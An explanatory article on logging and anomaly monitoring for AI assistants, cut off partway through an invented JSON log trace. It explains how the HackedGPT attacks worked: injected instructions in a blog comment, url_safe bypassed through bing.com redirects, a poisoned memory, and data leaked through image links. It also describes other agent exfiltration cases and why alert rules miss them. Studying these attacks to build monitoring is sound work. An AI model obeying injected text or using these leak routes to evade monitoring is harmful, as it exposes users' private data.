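# Logging and anomaly monitoring for AI assistants that browse, call tools and use connectors

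## How AI assistants act online and how they are compromised

An AI assistant is a language model (a program that produces text in response to text) with software that lets it take actions for a user. A few years ago, chatbots could only write replies. ChatGPT, Claude, Gemini and their competitors now also fetch web pages, keep notes on their users between conversations, and work in mailboxes, calendars and company file stores. A stranger who can put text where an assistant will read it, even in a blog comment, therefore has some chance of steering what the assistant does.

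Logging means keeping a record of each action an assistant takes, and anomaly monitoring means searching that record for unusual behaviour. Website operators have long done both, and since 2025 security writers have urged companies to do the same with their assistants.

### From a request to an action

A language model by itself produces only text. It can act because the surrounding software detects tool calls, which are requests in a fixed format to run a function such as fetching a page or sending an email. The software runs the function and returns the result to the model as more text.

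The Agentic AI Foundation's *MCP Usage Surged as the Protocol Went Stateless* (2026) gives an everyday example in which a user asks ChatGPT to help prepare for a meeting. The model receives the user's sentence and a list of the tools it may use. Its first output might be a tool call for tomorrow's calendar. The software runs the call, appends the result to everything the model has received so far, and runs the model again on the longer text. That text now includes the attendees' names, so the next call can search Slack for their recent messages. Later calls fetch related emails and then documents from Google Drive. When the model produces ordinary prose instead of a call, the software shows it to the user and the loop stops. Between the user's one sentence and the one answer, four services supplied data, and every call after the first could depend on text that earlier calls had returned.

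Many of these calls now travel over the Model Context Protocol (MCP), an open standard through which assistants find and call external tools. Its documentation gives the example of an assistant that reads its user's Google Calendar and Notion notes. Anthropic, the company that makes Claude, introduced MCP in late 2024 and donated it to the new Agentic AI Foundation a year later. By then, more than 10,000 active public servers offered tools through MCP, according to Anthropic's *Donating the Model Context Protocol and establishing the Agentic AI Foundation* (2025). In August 2026, ChatGPT users generated 98 times as many MCP calls as in January, according to the foundation.

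The July 2026 release announcement of the Model Context Protocol (2026) includes a sample call that is only a few lines long. It gives the method (a tool call), the tool ("search"), the argument (a query for "otters"), and the name and version of the application that sent it. The same release removed the protocol's session identifier, so each request is now sent independently, and linking the calls that belong to one user's request requires information from another source.

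Browsing, memory and connectors account for most of what an assistant can do beyond writing. An assistant browses when, for example, a user asks for a summary of an article at a given web address or asks a question that needs today's news. *HackedGPT* (2025), by the security company Tenable, found that ChatGPT's web tool had one command for searching and another for opening a page, and that the model could use either without an explicit request from the user.

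Memory is text that the assistant saves in one session (a continuous run on a user's request or conversation) and reads in later ones. ChatGPT's software adds saved memories to the system prompt, the standing instructions a model receives before the user's first message, so they affect every later conversation. In one of Tenable's tests, for example, the user had a saved memory asking for emojis in replies. Memory was on by default, and the model could save a memory without being asked.

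A connector is a standing, authorised link between the assistant and another service. The user signs in to a file store or mailbox once and grants access, and from then on the assistant can open files or messages there on its own. The tools page of the Model Context Protocol (2026) specification describes tools as "model-controlled". It recommends, but does not require, that a human always be able to refuse a call, and the protocol does not prescribe how the user should be asked. Someone who has to approve four lookups to prepare for one meeting will probably want to approve them all in advance.

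### Instructions hidden in what the assistant reads

In an indirect prompt injection, an attacker plants instructions in a web page, document or email. Someone else's assistant fetches that content during an ordinary task and follows the instructions as if its user had given them.

This attack works because a language model receives its instructions and its data as one long run of text, which includes the system prompt, the memories, the user's request and the fetched page. A well-built conventional program keeps instructions and data apart, so a sentence in a customer's address field does not become part of the program. Developers can put markers between the parts of a model's input and train the model to give less weight to commands in fetched material. Both measures make the attack less likely to succeed, but neither is a rule that the model cannot break, because the markers are themselves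 more input and the training only changes how probable each response is.

Stripping out everything that looks like an instruction would not help either, because users often want an assistant to act on instructions it finds, such as a set-up guide on a web page or a to-do list in an email. Whether an instruction is legitimate depends on who wrote it and what the user meant, which may not be clear from the words alone. In TechRadar's *Researchers claim ChatGPT has a whole host of worrying security flaws*, Moshe Bernstein of Tenable called this problem a fundamental weakness in how language models judge what information to trust. Tenable expected no systematic fix in the near future.

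An injected instruction does limited damage if the assistant has no data worth stealing and no way to send data out. The serious cases involve exfiltration, which means moving data to a party not entitled to it. Displaying a reply that contains an image can exfiltrate data without an email or an upload, because loading the image sends a request to the server at the image's address, and that request can carry information.

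### HackedGPT

Tenable's HackedGPT, published on 5 November 2025, describes seven vulnerabilities and attack techniques in ChatGPT, several of which the researchers combined into complete attacks. They did most of the work on GPT-4o and then confirmed that several of the results held on its successor, GPT-5. Tenable has a commercial interest in these findings because it sells monitoring for ChatGPT Enterprise, Claude, Gemini and Microsoft Copilot, as Help Net Security's *Tenable broadens AI visibility across major LLMs and AI tools* (2026) reports. Others had found similar problems. In its advisories, Tenable acknowledges a similar bypass of ChatGPT's link check, presented at Black Hat Europe in 2024, and a Guardian article from December 2024 on tests that manipulated ChatGPT's search tool.

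OpenAI had built defences against this sort of attack. ChatGPT passed the job of opening web pages to a second model, which identified itself as SearchGPT and had no access to the user's memories or conversation. A separate check, url_safe, examined most links and image addresses before ChatGPT displayed them and removed those it classed as unsafe. A hostile page might therefore trick SearchGPT, but that model held no private data, and url_safe should have stopped ChatGPT from loading an image from an attacker's server.

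Tenable bypassed the first defence through the conversation. SearchGPT's summary of a page became part of the chat, and ChatGPT received the whole chat again before each reply. Instructions that SearchGPT had copied into its summary therefore reached ChatGPT as part of ChatGPT's own earlier answers. A bug in how the ChatGPT website displayed code blocks hid the added text from the user.

Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* (2025) describes how a trusted domain defeated the link check. The check always allowed URLs at bing.com, but Bing's search results use bing.com URLs that redirect to other people's sites. Image links at bing.com could therefore lead to pages the researchers controlled. These links are fixed, so an attacker can't insert a stolen name or address into one. Instead, the choice of links and the order in which they loaded carried the data out, so a filter that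 scanned outgoing URLs for private text would have found none.

In the demonstration that used all of this, a user asks for a summary of a blog post that has a hostile comment under it. The table compares what the user would notice with the events a complete record would contain.

| Event | What the user sees | What a complete record would hold |
|---|---|---|
| The user asks for a summary | Their own message | The request and its time |
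| SearchGPT opens the blog post | Little or nothing | The page's address and its text, comment included |
| SearchGPT returns a summary | An ordinary summary | A longer text than the one on screen |
| The user sends a follow-up message | Their own message | A second request, with no mention of images |
| ChatGPT replies | A reply | Several image links to bing.com, and the redirects behind them |

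Logging only tool calls can miss the data leak in the last row. The chat window loads an image when it displays the reply, so the data can leave without the model calling any tool.

In another demonstration, SearchGPT's output led ChatGPT to save a memory to the effect that the user wanted private information sent out with every response. ChatGPT displayed a "Memory updated" notice, and each later reply, in any conversation, repeated the leak. An investigator examining one of those later sessions would find the leak but no hostile page, since the assistant had read that page days or weeks before. Tenable showed this variant only on GPT-4o, while its three other demonstrations (a phishing link added to a summary, the blog comment, and a site found through search) also worked on GPT-5.

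Some attacks did not require the victim to choose a malicious page. Tenable's *OpenAI SearchGPT Results Tampering with Prompt Injection* (2025) describes an attack in which the malicious site appeared among the search results for an innocent question. Another attack required one click on a link that opened ChatGPT and automatically submitted a prefilled prompt.

An attacker could take private information from the user's memories and chat history. The press material in KBI.Media's *Seven Critical Vulnerabilities Open ChatGPT to Data Theft and Hijacking* also lists data from connected services such as Google Drive or Gmail. Such theft is plausible for an assistant with those connectors, but the technical report does not demonstrate it. Tenable ran its tests on its own blogs and websites and reported no real victims.

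OpenAI's fixes are harder to determine. Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT Prompt Injection via ?q= Parameter in Web Interface* (2025) gives the clearest record, which covers the one-click link. Tenable reported the flaw on 15 April 2025, and by 30 April OpenAI had rolled out a fix to all users. On 6 May Tenable found the problem persisted. On 11 July OpenAI replied that it had added protections against automatic submission and improved its link check.

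The other three advisories list no fix. Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT “Command Memories” Injection via SearchGPT* describes the memory flaw as unpatched and records six requests for a status update but no reply. The advisories on the link check and on search results also report open problems, but all three timelines end in March 2025, eight months before HackedGPT appeared. At publication, Tenable said that OpenAI had fixed some of the vulnerabilities and that several remained active in GPT-5, but TechRadar noted that Tenable did not say which. The link-check bypass was probably still active, because the blog-comment attack depended on it and still worked on GPT-5, which OpenAI released in August 2025, after the July improvement.

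Tenable's *The Trifecta* (September 2025) described three since-fixed flaws in Google's Gemini that exposed private data. One was a "log-to-prompt injection", in which hostile text reached the assistant through a log.

### The advice to monitor assistants like internet-facing applications

HackedGPT prompted the advice that shaped this subject. AI News' *The enemy within* (2025), a trade-press article published the same day as HackedGPT, summarised Tenable's findings and advised companies on how to govern their assistants. Under the heading "Monitor like any internet-facing app", it recommends that a company watch an assistant as it would a public website, which anyone can reach and someone will eventually attack. The Digital Insider reposted the article under the same title.

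Under that heading the article asks firms to capture assistant actions and tool calls as structured logs, that is, as records with named fields that a machine can search. It then lists four things that should raise an alert:

- sudden spikes in browsing to unfamiliar domains
- attempts to summarise opaque code blocks
- unusual bursts of memory writes
- connector access outside policy boundaries

It also recommends injection tests before an assistant goes into use, a register of every assistant in the company, separate identities for people and assistants, and browsing only where a particular use needs it. It says staff should be ready to quarantine the assistant, clear its memory and change its credentials after a suspicious event. Clearing the memory makes sense given how the memory attack sustained itself.

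The article gives no thresholds for the alerts. For example, it does not specify how many new domains make a spike, over what period, or what makes a domain unfamiliar. It also gives no evidence that the alerts work, such as counts of the attacks they caught and the harmless sessions they flagged by mistake. The second alert is hard to interpret. It most likely stems from the display bug that hid text in a code block, but developers routinely ask assistants to explain obscure code. The fourth alert works only if someone has written down what each connector may be used for.

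As worded, the four alerts would probably have missed the HackedGPT attacks that prompted them. In the blog-comment attack, the assistant opened one page, possibly on a well-known site, so there was no spike. The user asked for a summary of a blog post, and the code block appeared only in the answer. The memory attack needed a single write rather than a burst, and none of the demonstrations used a connector. The data left through bing.com, a very familiar domain. The same sessions contained more telling signs: text in the summary that never appeared on screen, image links the user had not asked for, and a memory saved straight after the assistant had read a stranger's web page.

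## What web application monitoring offers, and where the comparison fails

The advice to monitor an assistant like any internet-facing app refers to practices that website operators have developed over about three decades. Some transfer to assistants almost unchanged, but others depend on facts about websites that are not true of assistants.

### How operators watch a public website

The simplest record is the access log. For every request, a web server adds a line with the time, the network address the request came from, the page requested and a code showing whether the server delivered it. An operator can see in this log that one address requested 4,000 pages in a minute. The log won't show that a logged-in customer opened another customer's invoice, because the server software has no record of who owns each invoice.

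The application behind the server does hold that information. The Open Worldwide Application Security Project (OWASP), a non-profit that publishes free guidance for developers, therefore names the application's own code as the primary source of security events in its *Logging Cheat Sheet*. OWASP says each entry should record "when, where, who and what". It recommends logging successful and failed logins, refused access, input that fails a check, and higher-risk actions such as exporting data or changing someone's privileges.

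It also recommends an interaction identifier, which developers more often call a correlation identifier: a value shared by all the log entries that result from one user action. For example, submitting one form might fail two checks at once and cause a database error some minutes later. The identifier links the three entries, so nobody has to guess from the timestamps that they are related.

A large site runs on many machines, so operators copy the logs to one place. OWASP's *Implement Security Logging and Monitoring* recommends a central, secure logging service, a common format and synchronised clocks. OWASP's *Application Logging Vocabulary Cheat Sheet* defines standard names for security events, so that one alert rule can search for the same term in every application.

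Logs achieve little if nobody looks at them. OWASP's *The Ten Most Critical Web Application Security Risks*, a widely used ranking, puts "Security Logging & Alerting Failures" ninth in its 2025 edition. For this edition, OWASP changed "Monitoring" in the category's name to "Alerting" because good logging without alerts is "of minimal value" in identifying incidents. The ranking draws on test data from more than 2.8 million applications, but automated tests can hardly measure this weakness, so it is on the list because practitioners voted for it in a survey.

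*Security Logging and Alerting Failures*, on myctrl.tools, reproduces the text of that category, which describes typical failures. A site might log successful logins but not failed ones, or a test attack might set off no alert. Staff may also receive so many false alarms that they overlook the real one. In one of its cases, a children's health plan learned from an outside party that an attacker had accessed and changed records, in a breach affecting more than 3.5 million children. Nobody had been logging or monitoring the system, and the breach could have gone on for more than seven years.

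Operators also try to stop attacks as they arrive, using a web application firewall that inspects each request before the application receives it. ModSecurity, a common open-source firewall, is often used with the Core Rule Set, a free collection of attack patterns. OWASP Core Rule Set's *The Top 5 Ways CRS Can Help You* (2017) calls the rule set a first line of defence and "no silver bullet". Each rule that a request matches adds points to the request's score, and the firewall blocks the request if the total reaches a threshold. OWASP Core Rule Set's *Paranoia Levels* explains that a separate setting, the paranoia level, controls how many rules are switched on. Higher levels also catch more innocent requests, and netnea's *Handling False Positives with the OWASP ModSecurity Core Rule Set* warns that a new installation at a high level can produce thousands of false alarms.

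A rate limit caps how many requests a client can make in a given period. A personal blog's summary of the OWASP ranking, *The Ten Most Critical Web Application Security Risks* (2026), lists rate limits as an access control that defends against automated attacks.

Firewalls and rate limits work with little information about what the application is for. OWASP's AppSensor project, which began in 2008, moves detection inside the application. Its introduction contrasts a bank, where someone who tries random doors will soon be led out, with the bank's website, where someone looking for weak points may go unnoticed. AppSensor defines more than 50 detection points, places in the code where the application can report something suspicious. An OWASP presentation gives examples: a customer who transfers 27 pounds and then tries 270,000, a user who changes the account number in a web address from their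 own to the next one, and a visitor who goes from step five of a process to step two. All of these requests can be well formed, so a firewall that looks for attack patterns would have little to match.

AppSensor can also respond automatically. In OWASP's example policy for developers, if a user tries three times within five minutes to open accounts they have no right to see, the software treats this as an attack and locks the user's own account. The method relies on attackers needing several tries. OWASP reasoned in the original AppSensor document that attackers can find many flaws only through trial and error, so an application that detects the attempts may be able to stop an attacker before they find a flaw.

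Decoy data, also called honeytokens, helps catch people looking where they have no reason to look. An operator might plant a fake administrator page or a fake account that no customer would use. Han, Kheir and Balzarotti tested decoys in *Evaluation of Deception-Based Web Attacks Detection* (2017). They added them to a working content management system for seven months, and its 258 regular users set off no false alarms. They then invited 150 people to attack a specially built online shop. The decoys caught 64% of those who exploited a flaw, but the rest got in without touching one. Decoys would do worse against automated scripts aimed at a known flaw, since a script sends only the request it needs.

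The table pairs each practice with its nearest use for an assistant.

| Practice | On a website | For an assistant |
|---|---|---|
| Access log | One line for each page request | One line for each tool call or page fetched |
| Application security log | Logins, refused access, data exports | Refused tool calls, memory writes, files opened through a connector |
| Correlation identifier | Links all entries from one click or form | Links a user's request to every call that followed from it |
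| Central collection and alerting | Combines the logs of many servers and notifies staff | Combines the logs of the assistant, its tools and the connected services |
| Web application firewall | Blocks requests that match attack patterns | Screens fetched text for injected instructions |
| Rate limit | Caps requests per client | Caps page fetches, memory writes or emails per session |
| Detection points in the application | Flag requests that make no sense for this application | Flag calls that make no sense for this user's request |
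| Decoy data | Fake accounts and pages that no customer uses | Fake files or contacts that no task needs |

Decoys produce few false alarms on a website because ordinary visitors never see them. But an assistant that searches a whole mailbox may well open a decoy email during a legitimate task. An alert would probably be more reliable if it fired when the decoy's contents were about to leave the company.

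### The argument for the comparison

Süleyman Özarslan, co-founder of the security vendor Picus Security, is among those who think web security methods should carry over. In *ChatGPT Bugs Put Private Data at Risk* (Underhill, 2025), an article for the trade site eSecurity Planet, he called the HackedGPT vulnerabilities "classic web application flaws repackaged for AI" and advised companies to hold their AI systems to the same security standards as every other internet-facing application.

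He did not set out an argument for monitoring in particular, but it would need roughly these premises:

1. Websites and assistants both take in text from people nobody has vetted.
2. Both act with privileges that an attacker lacks.
3. Software can recognise hostile input.
4. The attacker is a client of the system, whom the operator can identify and block.
5. Normal traffic is regular enough to model.
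6. The operator controls the logging.

The first two hold. David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC), gives an example in his December 2025 post *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*. A recruiter's system uses a language model to score CVs, and a candidate hides text in their CV telling the model to approve them for interview. The candidate can't approve anyone, but the system may be able to. Security specialists call such a system a confused deputy, meaning a program that someone with few privileges tricks into using its greater privileges on their behalf. A website with access to a customer database can also be a confused deputy.

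OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) describes the same combination in terms borrowed from conventional software security. An attacker needs a "source", a way to influence the system, and a "sink", a capability that becomes dangerous in the wrong context. In a web application, the source might be a form and the sink a database, while for an assistant they might be a web page and a mailbox connector. An assistant therefore needs monitoring at least as much as a website does, but whether the same methods will work depends on the other premises.

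### Recognising hostile input

SQL injection is the best-known attack on websites. SQL is the language programs use to give commands to databases, and it has a strict grammar. A carelessly written website inserts a visitor's text directly into a command, so the visitor can type something that the database will treat as part of the command. The attack works only if the resulting command is valid SQL, so firewalls can check for fragments of SQL where a name or a date should be.

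Even with that advantage, web application firewalls miss some attacks. *Protecting Web Applications using a Multimodal AI-based System* (2026) reports a test in which a scanning tool sent 901 SQL injection inputs to a test application behind the ModSecurity firewall, with the Core Rule Set at its default level. The firewall missed 109 of them, catching about 88%. In *ModSec-Learn* (2024), which used different data and the next stricter level, ModSecurity caught about 75% of the attacks with its threshold set to flag 1% of legitimate requests.

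Websites can tolerate those misses because they have a better defence behind the firewall, the parameterised query. The developer gives the database a command with a gap in it and supplies the visitor's text separately. The database never interprets that text as a command, whatever it contains. According to David C, SQL injection attacks peaked around 2010 and are now rare on websites, after a decade of breaches led to better defaults.

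David C's central claim is that prompt injection probably has no fix equivalent to parameterised queries. Those work because a database already treats commands and data differently, and a language model has no such boundary for a developer to enforce. He therefore calls a language model an "inherently confusable deputy" and advises developers to limit its actions through ordinary code that it cannot override. If a system can't tolerate the remaining risk, he thinks it may be a poor use for a language model.

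He also warns against blocking known bad phrases, the method most like a firewall rule. An attacker can reword an English instruction in endless ways without changing its meaning, while an SQL fragment has to remain valid SQL.

OpenAI has come to a similar view. In a December 2025 post quoted by Fortune (2025), it said prompt injection was "unlikely to ever be fully 'solved'". OpenAI has some interest in lowering expectations of its own products, but the NCSC does not sell an assistant. In its 2026 post on resisting prompt injection, OpenAI added that filters that classify incoming text as hostile or harmless do not usually catch fully developed attacks. It compared the filter's task to detecting a lie, often without the necessary context. In 2025, outside researchers reported an attack email that read like a routine follow-up about a company restructuring and worked in half of the tests.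 To recognise it, a filter would have to know whether the sender had a legitimate reason to make such a request, which could not be determined from the email alone.

So a monitor that only reads incoming text is weaker for an assistant than for a website. Checking what the assistant is about to send can improve it. OpenAI describes a safeguard called Safe Url, designed to detect when information from a conversation would be sent to a third party. ChatGPT then either shows the user the information and asks for confirmation, or blocks the transfer. This can work even if nobody recognises the injection, but the check must still detect the leak, which is harder when the data is encoded in the choice of links, as it was in HackedGPT.

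### Identifying and blocking the attacker

AppSensor locks an account on the assumption that the person using it is the attacker. Rate limits and lists of banned addresses work on a similar assumption. In a prompt injection, however, a third party ("not the user nor the AI", as OpenAI's *Understanding prompt injections* puts it) misleads the model. The attacker may never connect to the company's systems, and the account in the log belongs to the victim.

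Suppose a company applied the three-strikes rule to its assistant. An employee asks for a summary of a web page, and hidden instructions on the page make the assistant try to open three files the employee isn't allowed to access. The rule locks the employee out, so an attacker can lock out staff by publishing a web page. For websites, OWASP's cheat sheet advises developers that if log data can trigger action against users, they should make sure nobody can exploit it to deny service to others. For an assistant, ending the session or suspending its connectors would be safer than locking the account.

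The company could also block the source of the text. That may be easy if the source is an obscure domain, but if the text was a comment on a popular site or an email from a customer, blocking the source could also cut off legitimate content. The company also needs a log that shows which piece of text led to which action.

Websites sometimes have this problem too. In cross-site request forgery, a hostile page causes a visitor's browser to send a request to another site where the visitor is logged in. The second site's log records the request as coming from the innocent visitor, much as an assistant's log would. Developers largely solved this by having the site's genuine pages include a secret value with each sensitive request, because the hostile page cannot supply that value. The same defense would not stop a prompt injection, because the malicious tool call comes from the genuine assistant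 with valid credentials.

David C expects that attackers will usually have to refine an attack, and suggests that failed tool calls could reveal one early. This applies AppSensor's reasoning to a language model. It seems sound for an assistant that a company has built for itself, whose internal tools outsiders can test only by attacking them. It is less convincing for a product like ChatGPT, because an attacker can open an account and practise on their own web pages, as Tenable did. The failures then appear in the vendor's logs, and the victim's company might see only the version that works.

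### Modelling normal traffic

A web application has a limited set of pages and forms, and its developers know what belongs in each field and the order of the steps. AppSensor can therefore flag step two occurring after step five without using statistics.

Learning what is normal from traffic is harder. *WAPP* (2026) tests a system that derives firewall rules from a site's live requests. Each rule describes what a legitimate value looks like, and the firewall rejects everything else. The system scores each rule by the strength of its evidence. In a controlled test with artificial data, rules scoring 0.5873 or more blocked no legitimate values, while those scoring 0.4787 or less blocked 60 of 108. But one rule for usernames, a short text field on a single form, scored 0.7709 and still blocked 28 of 43 legitimate names, along with all 13 genuine attacks. Further validation lowered its score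 to 0.5709, below the cutoff.

An assistant's behaviour is less predictable than a web application's. Two employees who ask for help preparing for a meeting may trigger quite different tool calls. The same employee may ask about tax law in the morning and a holiday in the afternoon, with unfamiliar domains in both sessions. A new tool or model can suddenly change the pattern for everyone. Since real attacks are rare, even a small false positive rate could fill the alert queue with harmless sessions.

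Normal behaviour is probably predictable for some assistants but not for others. An assistant that only matches invoices to orders should be almost as predictable as a web form, and a call to an outside website would stand out. A general assistant with a browser and six connectors has a much wider range of normal behaviour, so rules about particular combinations of events may be more useful than a model of typical traffic.

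### Controlling the logs

A website operator can usually decide what to log, because the operator's developers write the application or at least install it. If a field is missing, they can add it. OWASP's advice to record events in the application's own code depends on this access.

When a company subscribes to ChatGPT or Claude, the vendor runs the software and decides which events the company can see, in how much detail and for how long. Some steps may leave no record that the company can obtain. OWASP advises treating logs from outside one's own systems as untrusted, since entries may be missing, altered or forged. For a hosted assistant, that advice could apply to most of the evidence.

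Companies that moved their websites to other firms' servers have faced this problem too. In one case in the OWASP category, attackers took personal data on millions of a large Indian airline's passengers, including passport and credit card details, from a cloud hosting provider. The airline learned of the breach only when the provider told it some time later. A company that builds its own assistant and only rents the model is in a better position, because its own software runs the tool calls and can log them all.

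### Where the two views differ in practice

Özarslan's description fits much of HackedGPT. Web developers have dealt with misused redirects like the bing.com links for years. The display bug was ordinary, and the one-click link resembled cross-site request forgery. Conventional fixes exist for all of these, and Underhill recommends some, including tighter redirect checks and strong authorisation for memory writes. Tenable's complete attacks relied on such flaws to get data out or to hide what was happening, so fixing them would have stopped or exposed several demonstrations.

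But SearchGPT also followed instructions in a stranger's comment, and that problem has no conventional fix. David C worries that people with a background in web security will expect one. They may then buy a product that promises to stop prompt injection and give the assistant privileges that only a system without the flaw should have. He fears a wave of breaches like the one that followed the spread of SQL databases across the web.

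Özarslan also recommends zero-trust architecture, which means checking every request, even those from inside the company. This fits David C's advice to restrict what a confused assistant can do. Both would have companies limit the assistant's access, and neither treats monitoring as a substitute for that.

OWASP and David C would probably differ more over what a log entry should hold. For web applications, OWASP expects most entries to contain an extract or a few summary properties, with full content as the exception. That is often enough for a failed login or a refused page. David C suggests that an assistant's log may need the model's full input and output, as well as its tool use and API calls. The evidence of a prompt injection may be one sentence in a long web page, which a summary could easily leave out.

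## What the log of an assistant's actions should contain

A company designing a log has to decide which facts about each action to store and in which named fields, as well as whether to keep a short extract or the model's full input and output. Investigators can rarely recover a missing field later, so a good way to judge a field is to ask which question they couldn't answer without it.

### Log entries and traces

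A log entry records one action, such as a tool call, a page fetch or a memory write, with each fact in its own named field. A trace links the entries from one session to show which step led to which. For example, an entry might show that the assistant sent an email, while the trace shows that it had just read a stranger's document.

A chat transcript is a poor substitute for either. It holds the messages on the user's screen, which leave out most tool calls and may also leave out parts of replies, as the display bug in HackedGPT showed. People can also alter it. Lumia Security tested the desktop apps for Claude, ChatGPT and Microsoft Copilot and found that an attacker with a login token stolen from one of these apps could change the victim's conversation history to cover their tracks. The US non-profit MITRE describes the test in a case study in ATLAS, its public catalogue of attacks on AI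 systems and defences against them.

The software that runs the tool calls should write the log entries, rather than the model. When the model reports "I've emailed the summary to Tom", that statement may be wrong or reflect hostile text the model has read. The Australian Signals Directorate's *Careful adoption of agentic AI services* (2026), written with partner agencies in the US, Canada, New Zealand and the UK, recommends independent monitoring systems that check agents' reports against system logs.

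Developers print debugging output to find faults. It is usually free text, its wording changes between releases, and developers delete it once the fault is gone. Performance data is more orderly. OpenTelemetry, an open-source project, sets common formats for it, based on the span, a timed record of one operation. But engineers often keep only a sample of their traces to save money, and OpenTelemetry's *Semantic conventions for generative client AI spans* lists the fields that matter when choosing which traces to keep. A sample of one session in a hundred is enough to show that an assistant has become slow, but it would probably not include the session in which the assistant leaked a file, so a security log has to cover every session.

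### The questions an entry should answer

Every entry needs a timestamp, its own identifier and a session identifier. Since MCP no longer provides a session identifier, the assistant's software has to supply one. The remaining fields cover seven questions.

**Who asked?** The entry should identify the person whose request started the session and link to the exact words of the request. Some assistants, however, start work without a user. In another of MITRE's case studies, the security company Zenity built a customer service agent in Microsoft's Copilot Studio that watched an inbox, looked up each sender's history and emailed the right consultant. Zenity's researchers wrote to that inbox as outsiders and got the agent to send them private customer data through its email tool, an issue Microsoft has since fixed. No employee had asked for anything, so naming the inbox owner as the user in the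 log would implicate an innocent person. A better entry would record that an incoming email started the session, and who sent it.

The log should identify the assistant and record the versions of its model, system prompt and surrounding software, because each can change separately. OpenTelemetry has one field for the model requested and another for the model that responded, with "gpt-4" and "gpt-4-0613" as examples. Recording the exact version lets a company find other sessions that ran on it. Even with that version, an investigator can't reliably reproduce an incident to fill in what the log left out, because the same prompt can lead to different actions, as the Five Eyes agencies point out.

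**Under whose authority did it act?** Each entry should identify the permission the assistant used, who gave it, what it covers and when it expires. An employee delegates authority by connecting their mailbox, an administrator may do so for a whole company, and an assistant may in turn delegate part of a task to another assistant. In a scenario from the Five Eyes guidance, an agent that installs security patches can write to any file. Someone outside the IT group asks it to apply a patch and clean up the firewall logs, and it does both. If the log recorded only the agent's identity, the deletion would look authorised. Recording the user's identity alongside the permission would show that the person asking had no right to delete those files.

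The log should record which tool the assistant called and with which arguments. The tool's name shows that an email went out, but the recipients, text and attachments are in the arguments. Without them, a leak looks the same as a routine message.

The log should contain what each tool returned, not only a status of "success", because a hostile tool can mix instructions into real results and, as MITRE notes, appear to work normally. Sometimes the harm is in the assistant's answer alone. In a 2024 test on Microsoft 365 Copilot, Zenity sent an email that caused the assistant to give a user the wrong bank details for a payment, with a citation that made them look trustworthy. The evidence would have been in the documents that the search returned and the one that the answer cited, and a log of outgoing messages would have contained nothing suspicious.

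The entry should record whether the call was allowed or denied, which rule and version decided this, and when the check was made, which may differ from the time of the call. In another Five Eyes scenario, a customer support system checks permissions only once, when it starts. An attacker later takes over one of its components, and the agent keeps using the old approvals for account changes that should each need a new check. Every entry would correctly show the call as allowed, so a reviewer could find the problem only from the time of the check.

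The log entry for each call should identify the text that was in the model's input at the time. To avoid copying the whole input into every entry, the software can store each piece of text once and list which pieces were present. Automatic detectors may or may not need this text, but a person investigating a prompt injection can hardly do without it.

### Extra fields for pages, memories and connectors

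For a page fetch, the log should keep the full address, since the part after the domain name can contain stolen data. In a 2023 test by the security blog Embrace the Red, also in MITRE's catalogue, Google's Bard displayed an image whose address contained the user's conversation. The address was on a domain that Google owned. A log of domain names would have recorded only that a Google product had contacted Google. (Google has fixed this flaw.)

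The entry should also list every address in a chain of redirects, because the first may belong to a trusted site and the last to an attacker, as with the bing.com links in HackedGPT. It should also record whether the link came from the user, a search result, another page or a saved memory. An unfamiliar website is much more suspicious if its address came from a stranger's email than if the user typed it.

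The log entry for a memory write should contain the old text, the new text and the source. MITRE advises companies to record the source of every memory update and keep a history with known good versions, so that they can reverse a suspicious change. Without the old text, staff could delete a bad memory but not restore the one it replaced. The source helps an investigator trace a recurring leak, like the one in the HackedGPT memory demonstration, back to the hostile page. This works if each session's log lists the memories loaded into the session and each memory links to the log entry that created it.

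Connector calls need three further fields:

- the account, since one employee may have connected two mailboxes, or a whole team may share one login
- the scope, meaning what the connector had permission to do at that moment, such as reading mail but not sending it
- the identifiers of the files or messages that the assistant opened, because "searched the mailbox" could mean one message or ten thousand

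Scope and identifiers are most useful together, because a company can then compare what an assistant may open with what it does open. This could reveal a bot like the one mentioned in the Five Eyes guidance, a calendar bot that can read everyone's meetings when it needs only those of the person asking. Recording who wrote each item also helps, because a file in the company's own store may have come from a supplier, and an email in an employee's inbox usually came from someone else.

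### Denied calls and changed tool descriptions

The log should include denied calls, even though they have no effect. A refusal can give early warning of an attack and can explain the call that follows it in the same session. The component that refused the call has to write the entry, because the call never reached the tool and so won't appear in the tool's own log.

*Agent Audit Trail* (Sharif, 2026) proposes a logging format to the Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), which sets many of the internet's technical standards. The format requires software to record a decision to deny an action before the action would have run. Sharif argues that an entry written afterwards can't prove that a check was in place beforehand. For systems that the EU's AI Act classes as high-risk, the format requires two entries for any action that changes something outside the assistant, one for the authorisation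 and one for the result.

Many refusals have innocent causes. For example, a model may request a tool that the company has switched off or guess at a file it cannot open. Reason codes help to sort refusals. Sharif defines nine, including one for an agent that lacks a permission and one for an agent with a revoked identity. The log should also include refusals by people. The Five Eyes agencies recommend prioritizing high-risk incidents, including actions that human reviewers have denied.

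The log should include tool descriptions, which are easy to overlook. Each tool comes with a short text explaining what it does, and the model reads this text to decide which tool to use and how. With an outside MCP server, a stranger writes this part of the model's input. The Five Eyes agencies note that models choose tools with persuasive descriptions more often. A description can also change after a company has approved the tool. MITRE describes attackers who publish harmless versions first, build a reputation and then release a malicious update.

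A tool's description can change while its name stays the same, so a log that records only the name won't show the change. The software should store the full description whenever it changes and note in each entry which version was current. It should do this for every tool available to the model, including those the model didn't call, because instructions in one tool's description can affect how the model uses another.

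### A harmless request that becomes a leak

In the invented trace below, Maya asks her company's assistant to summarise a supplier's proposal and send the summary to her colleague Tom. Fields that apply to the whole session appear once, at the top. The numbers under "from" identify the entry that supplied each argument, and names such as "stored-881" refer to text kept separately.

```json
{
  "session": "s-4471",
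  "user": "maya@firm.example",
  "assistant": "office-assistant 3.2",
  "grant": {
    "given_by": "maya@firm.example",
    "scope": ["files.read", "files.share", "mail.send"],
    "expires": "2027-03-01"
  },
  "entries": [
    {
      "id": 1, "time": "09:14:02", "type": "user_request",
      "text": "Summarise the attached proposal and send the summary to tom@firm.example.",
      "attached": "file-203"
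    },
    {
      "id": 2, "time": "09:14:05", "tool": "files.read",
      "arguments": {"file": "file-203"},
      "from": {"file": 1},
      "decision": "allowed", "rule": "read-files",
      "result": {"author": "sales@norwood.example", "text": "stored-881"}
    },
    {
      "id": 3, "time": "09:14:09", "tool": "files.search",
      "arguments": {"query": "supplier prices"},
      "from": {"query": 2},
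      "decision": "allowed", "rule": "read-files",
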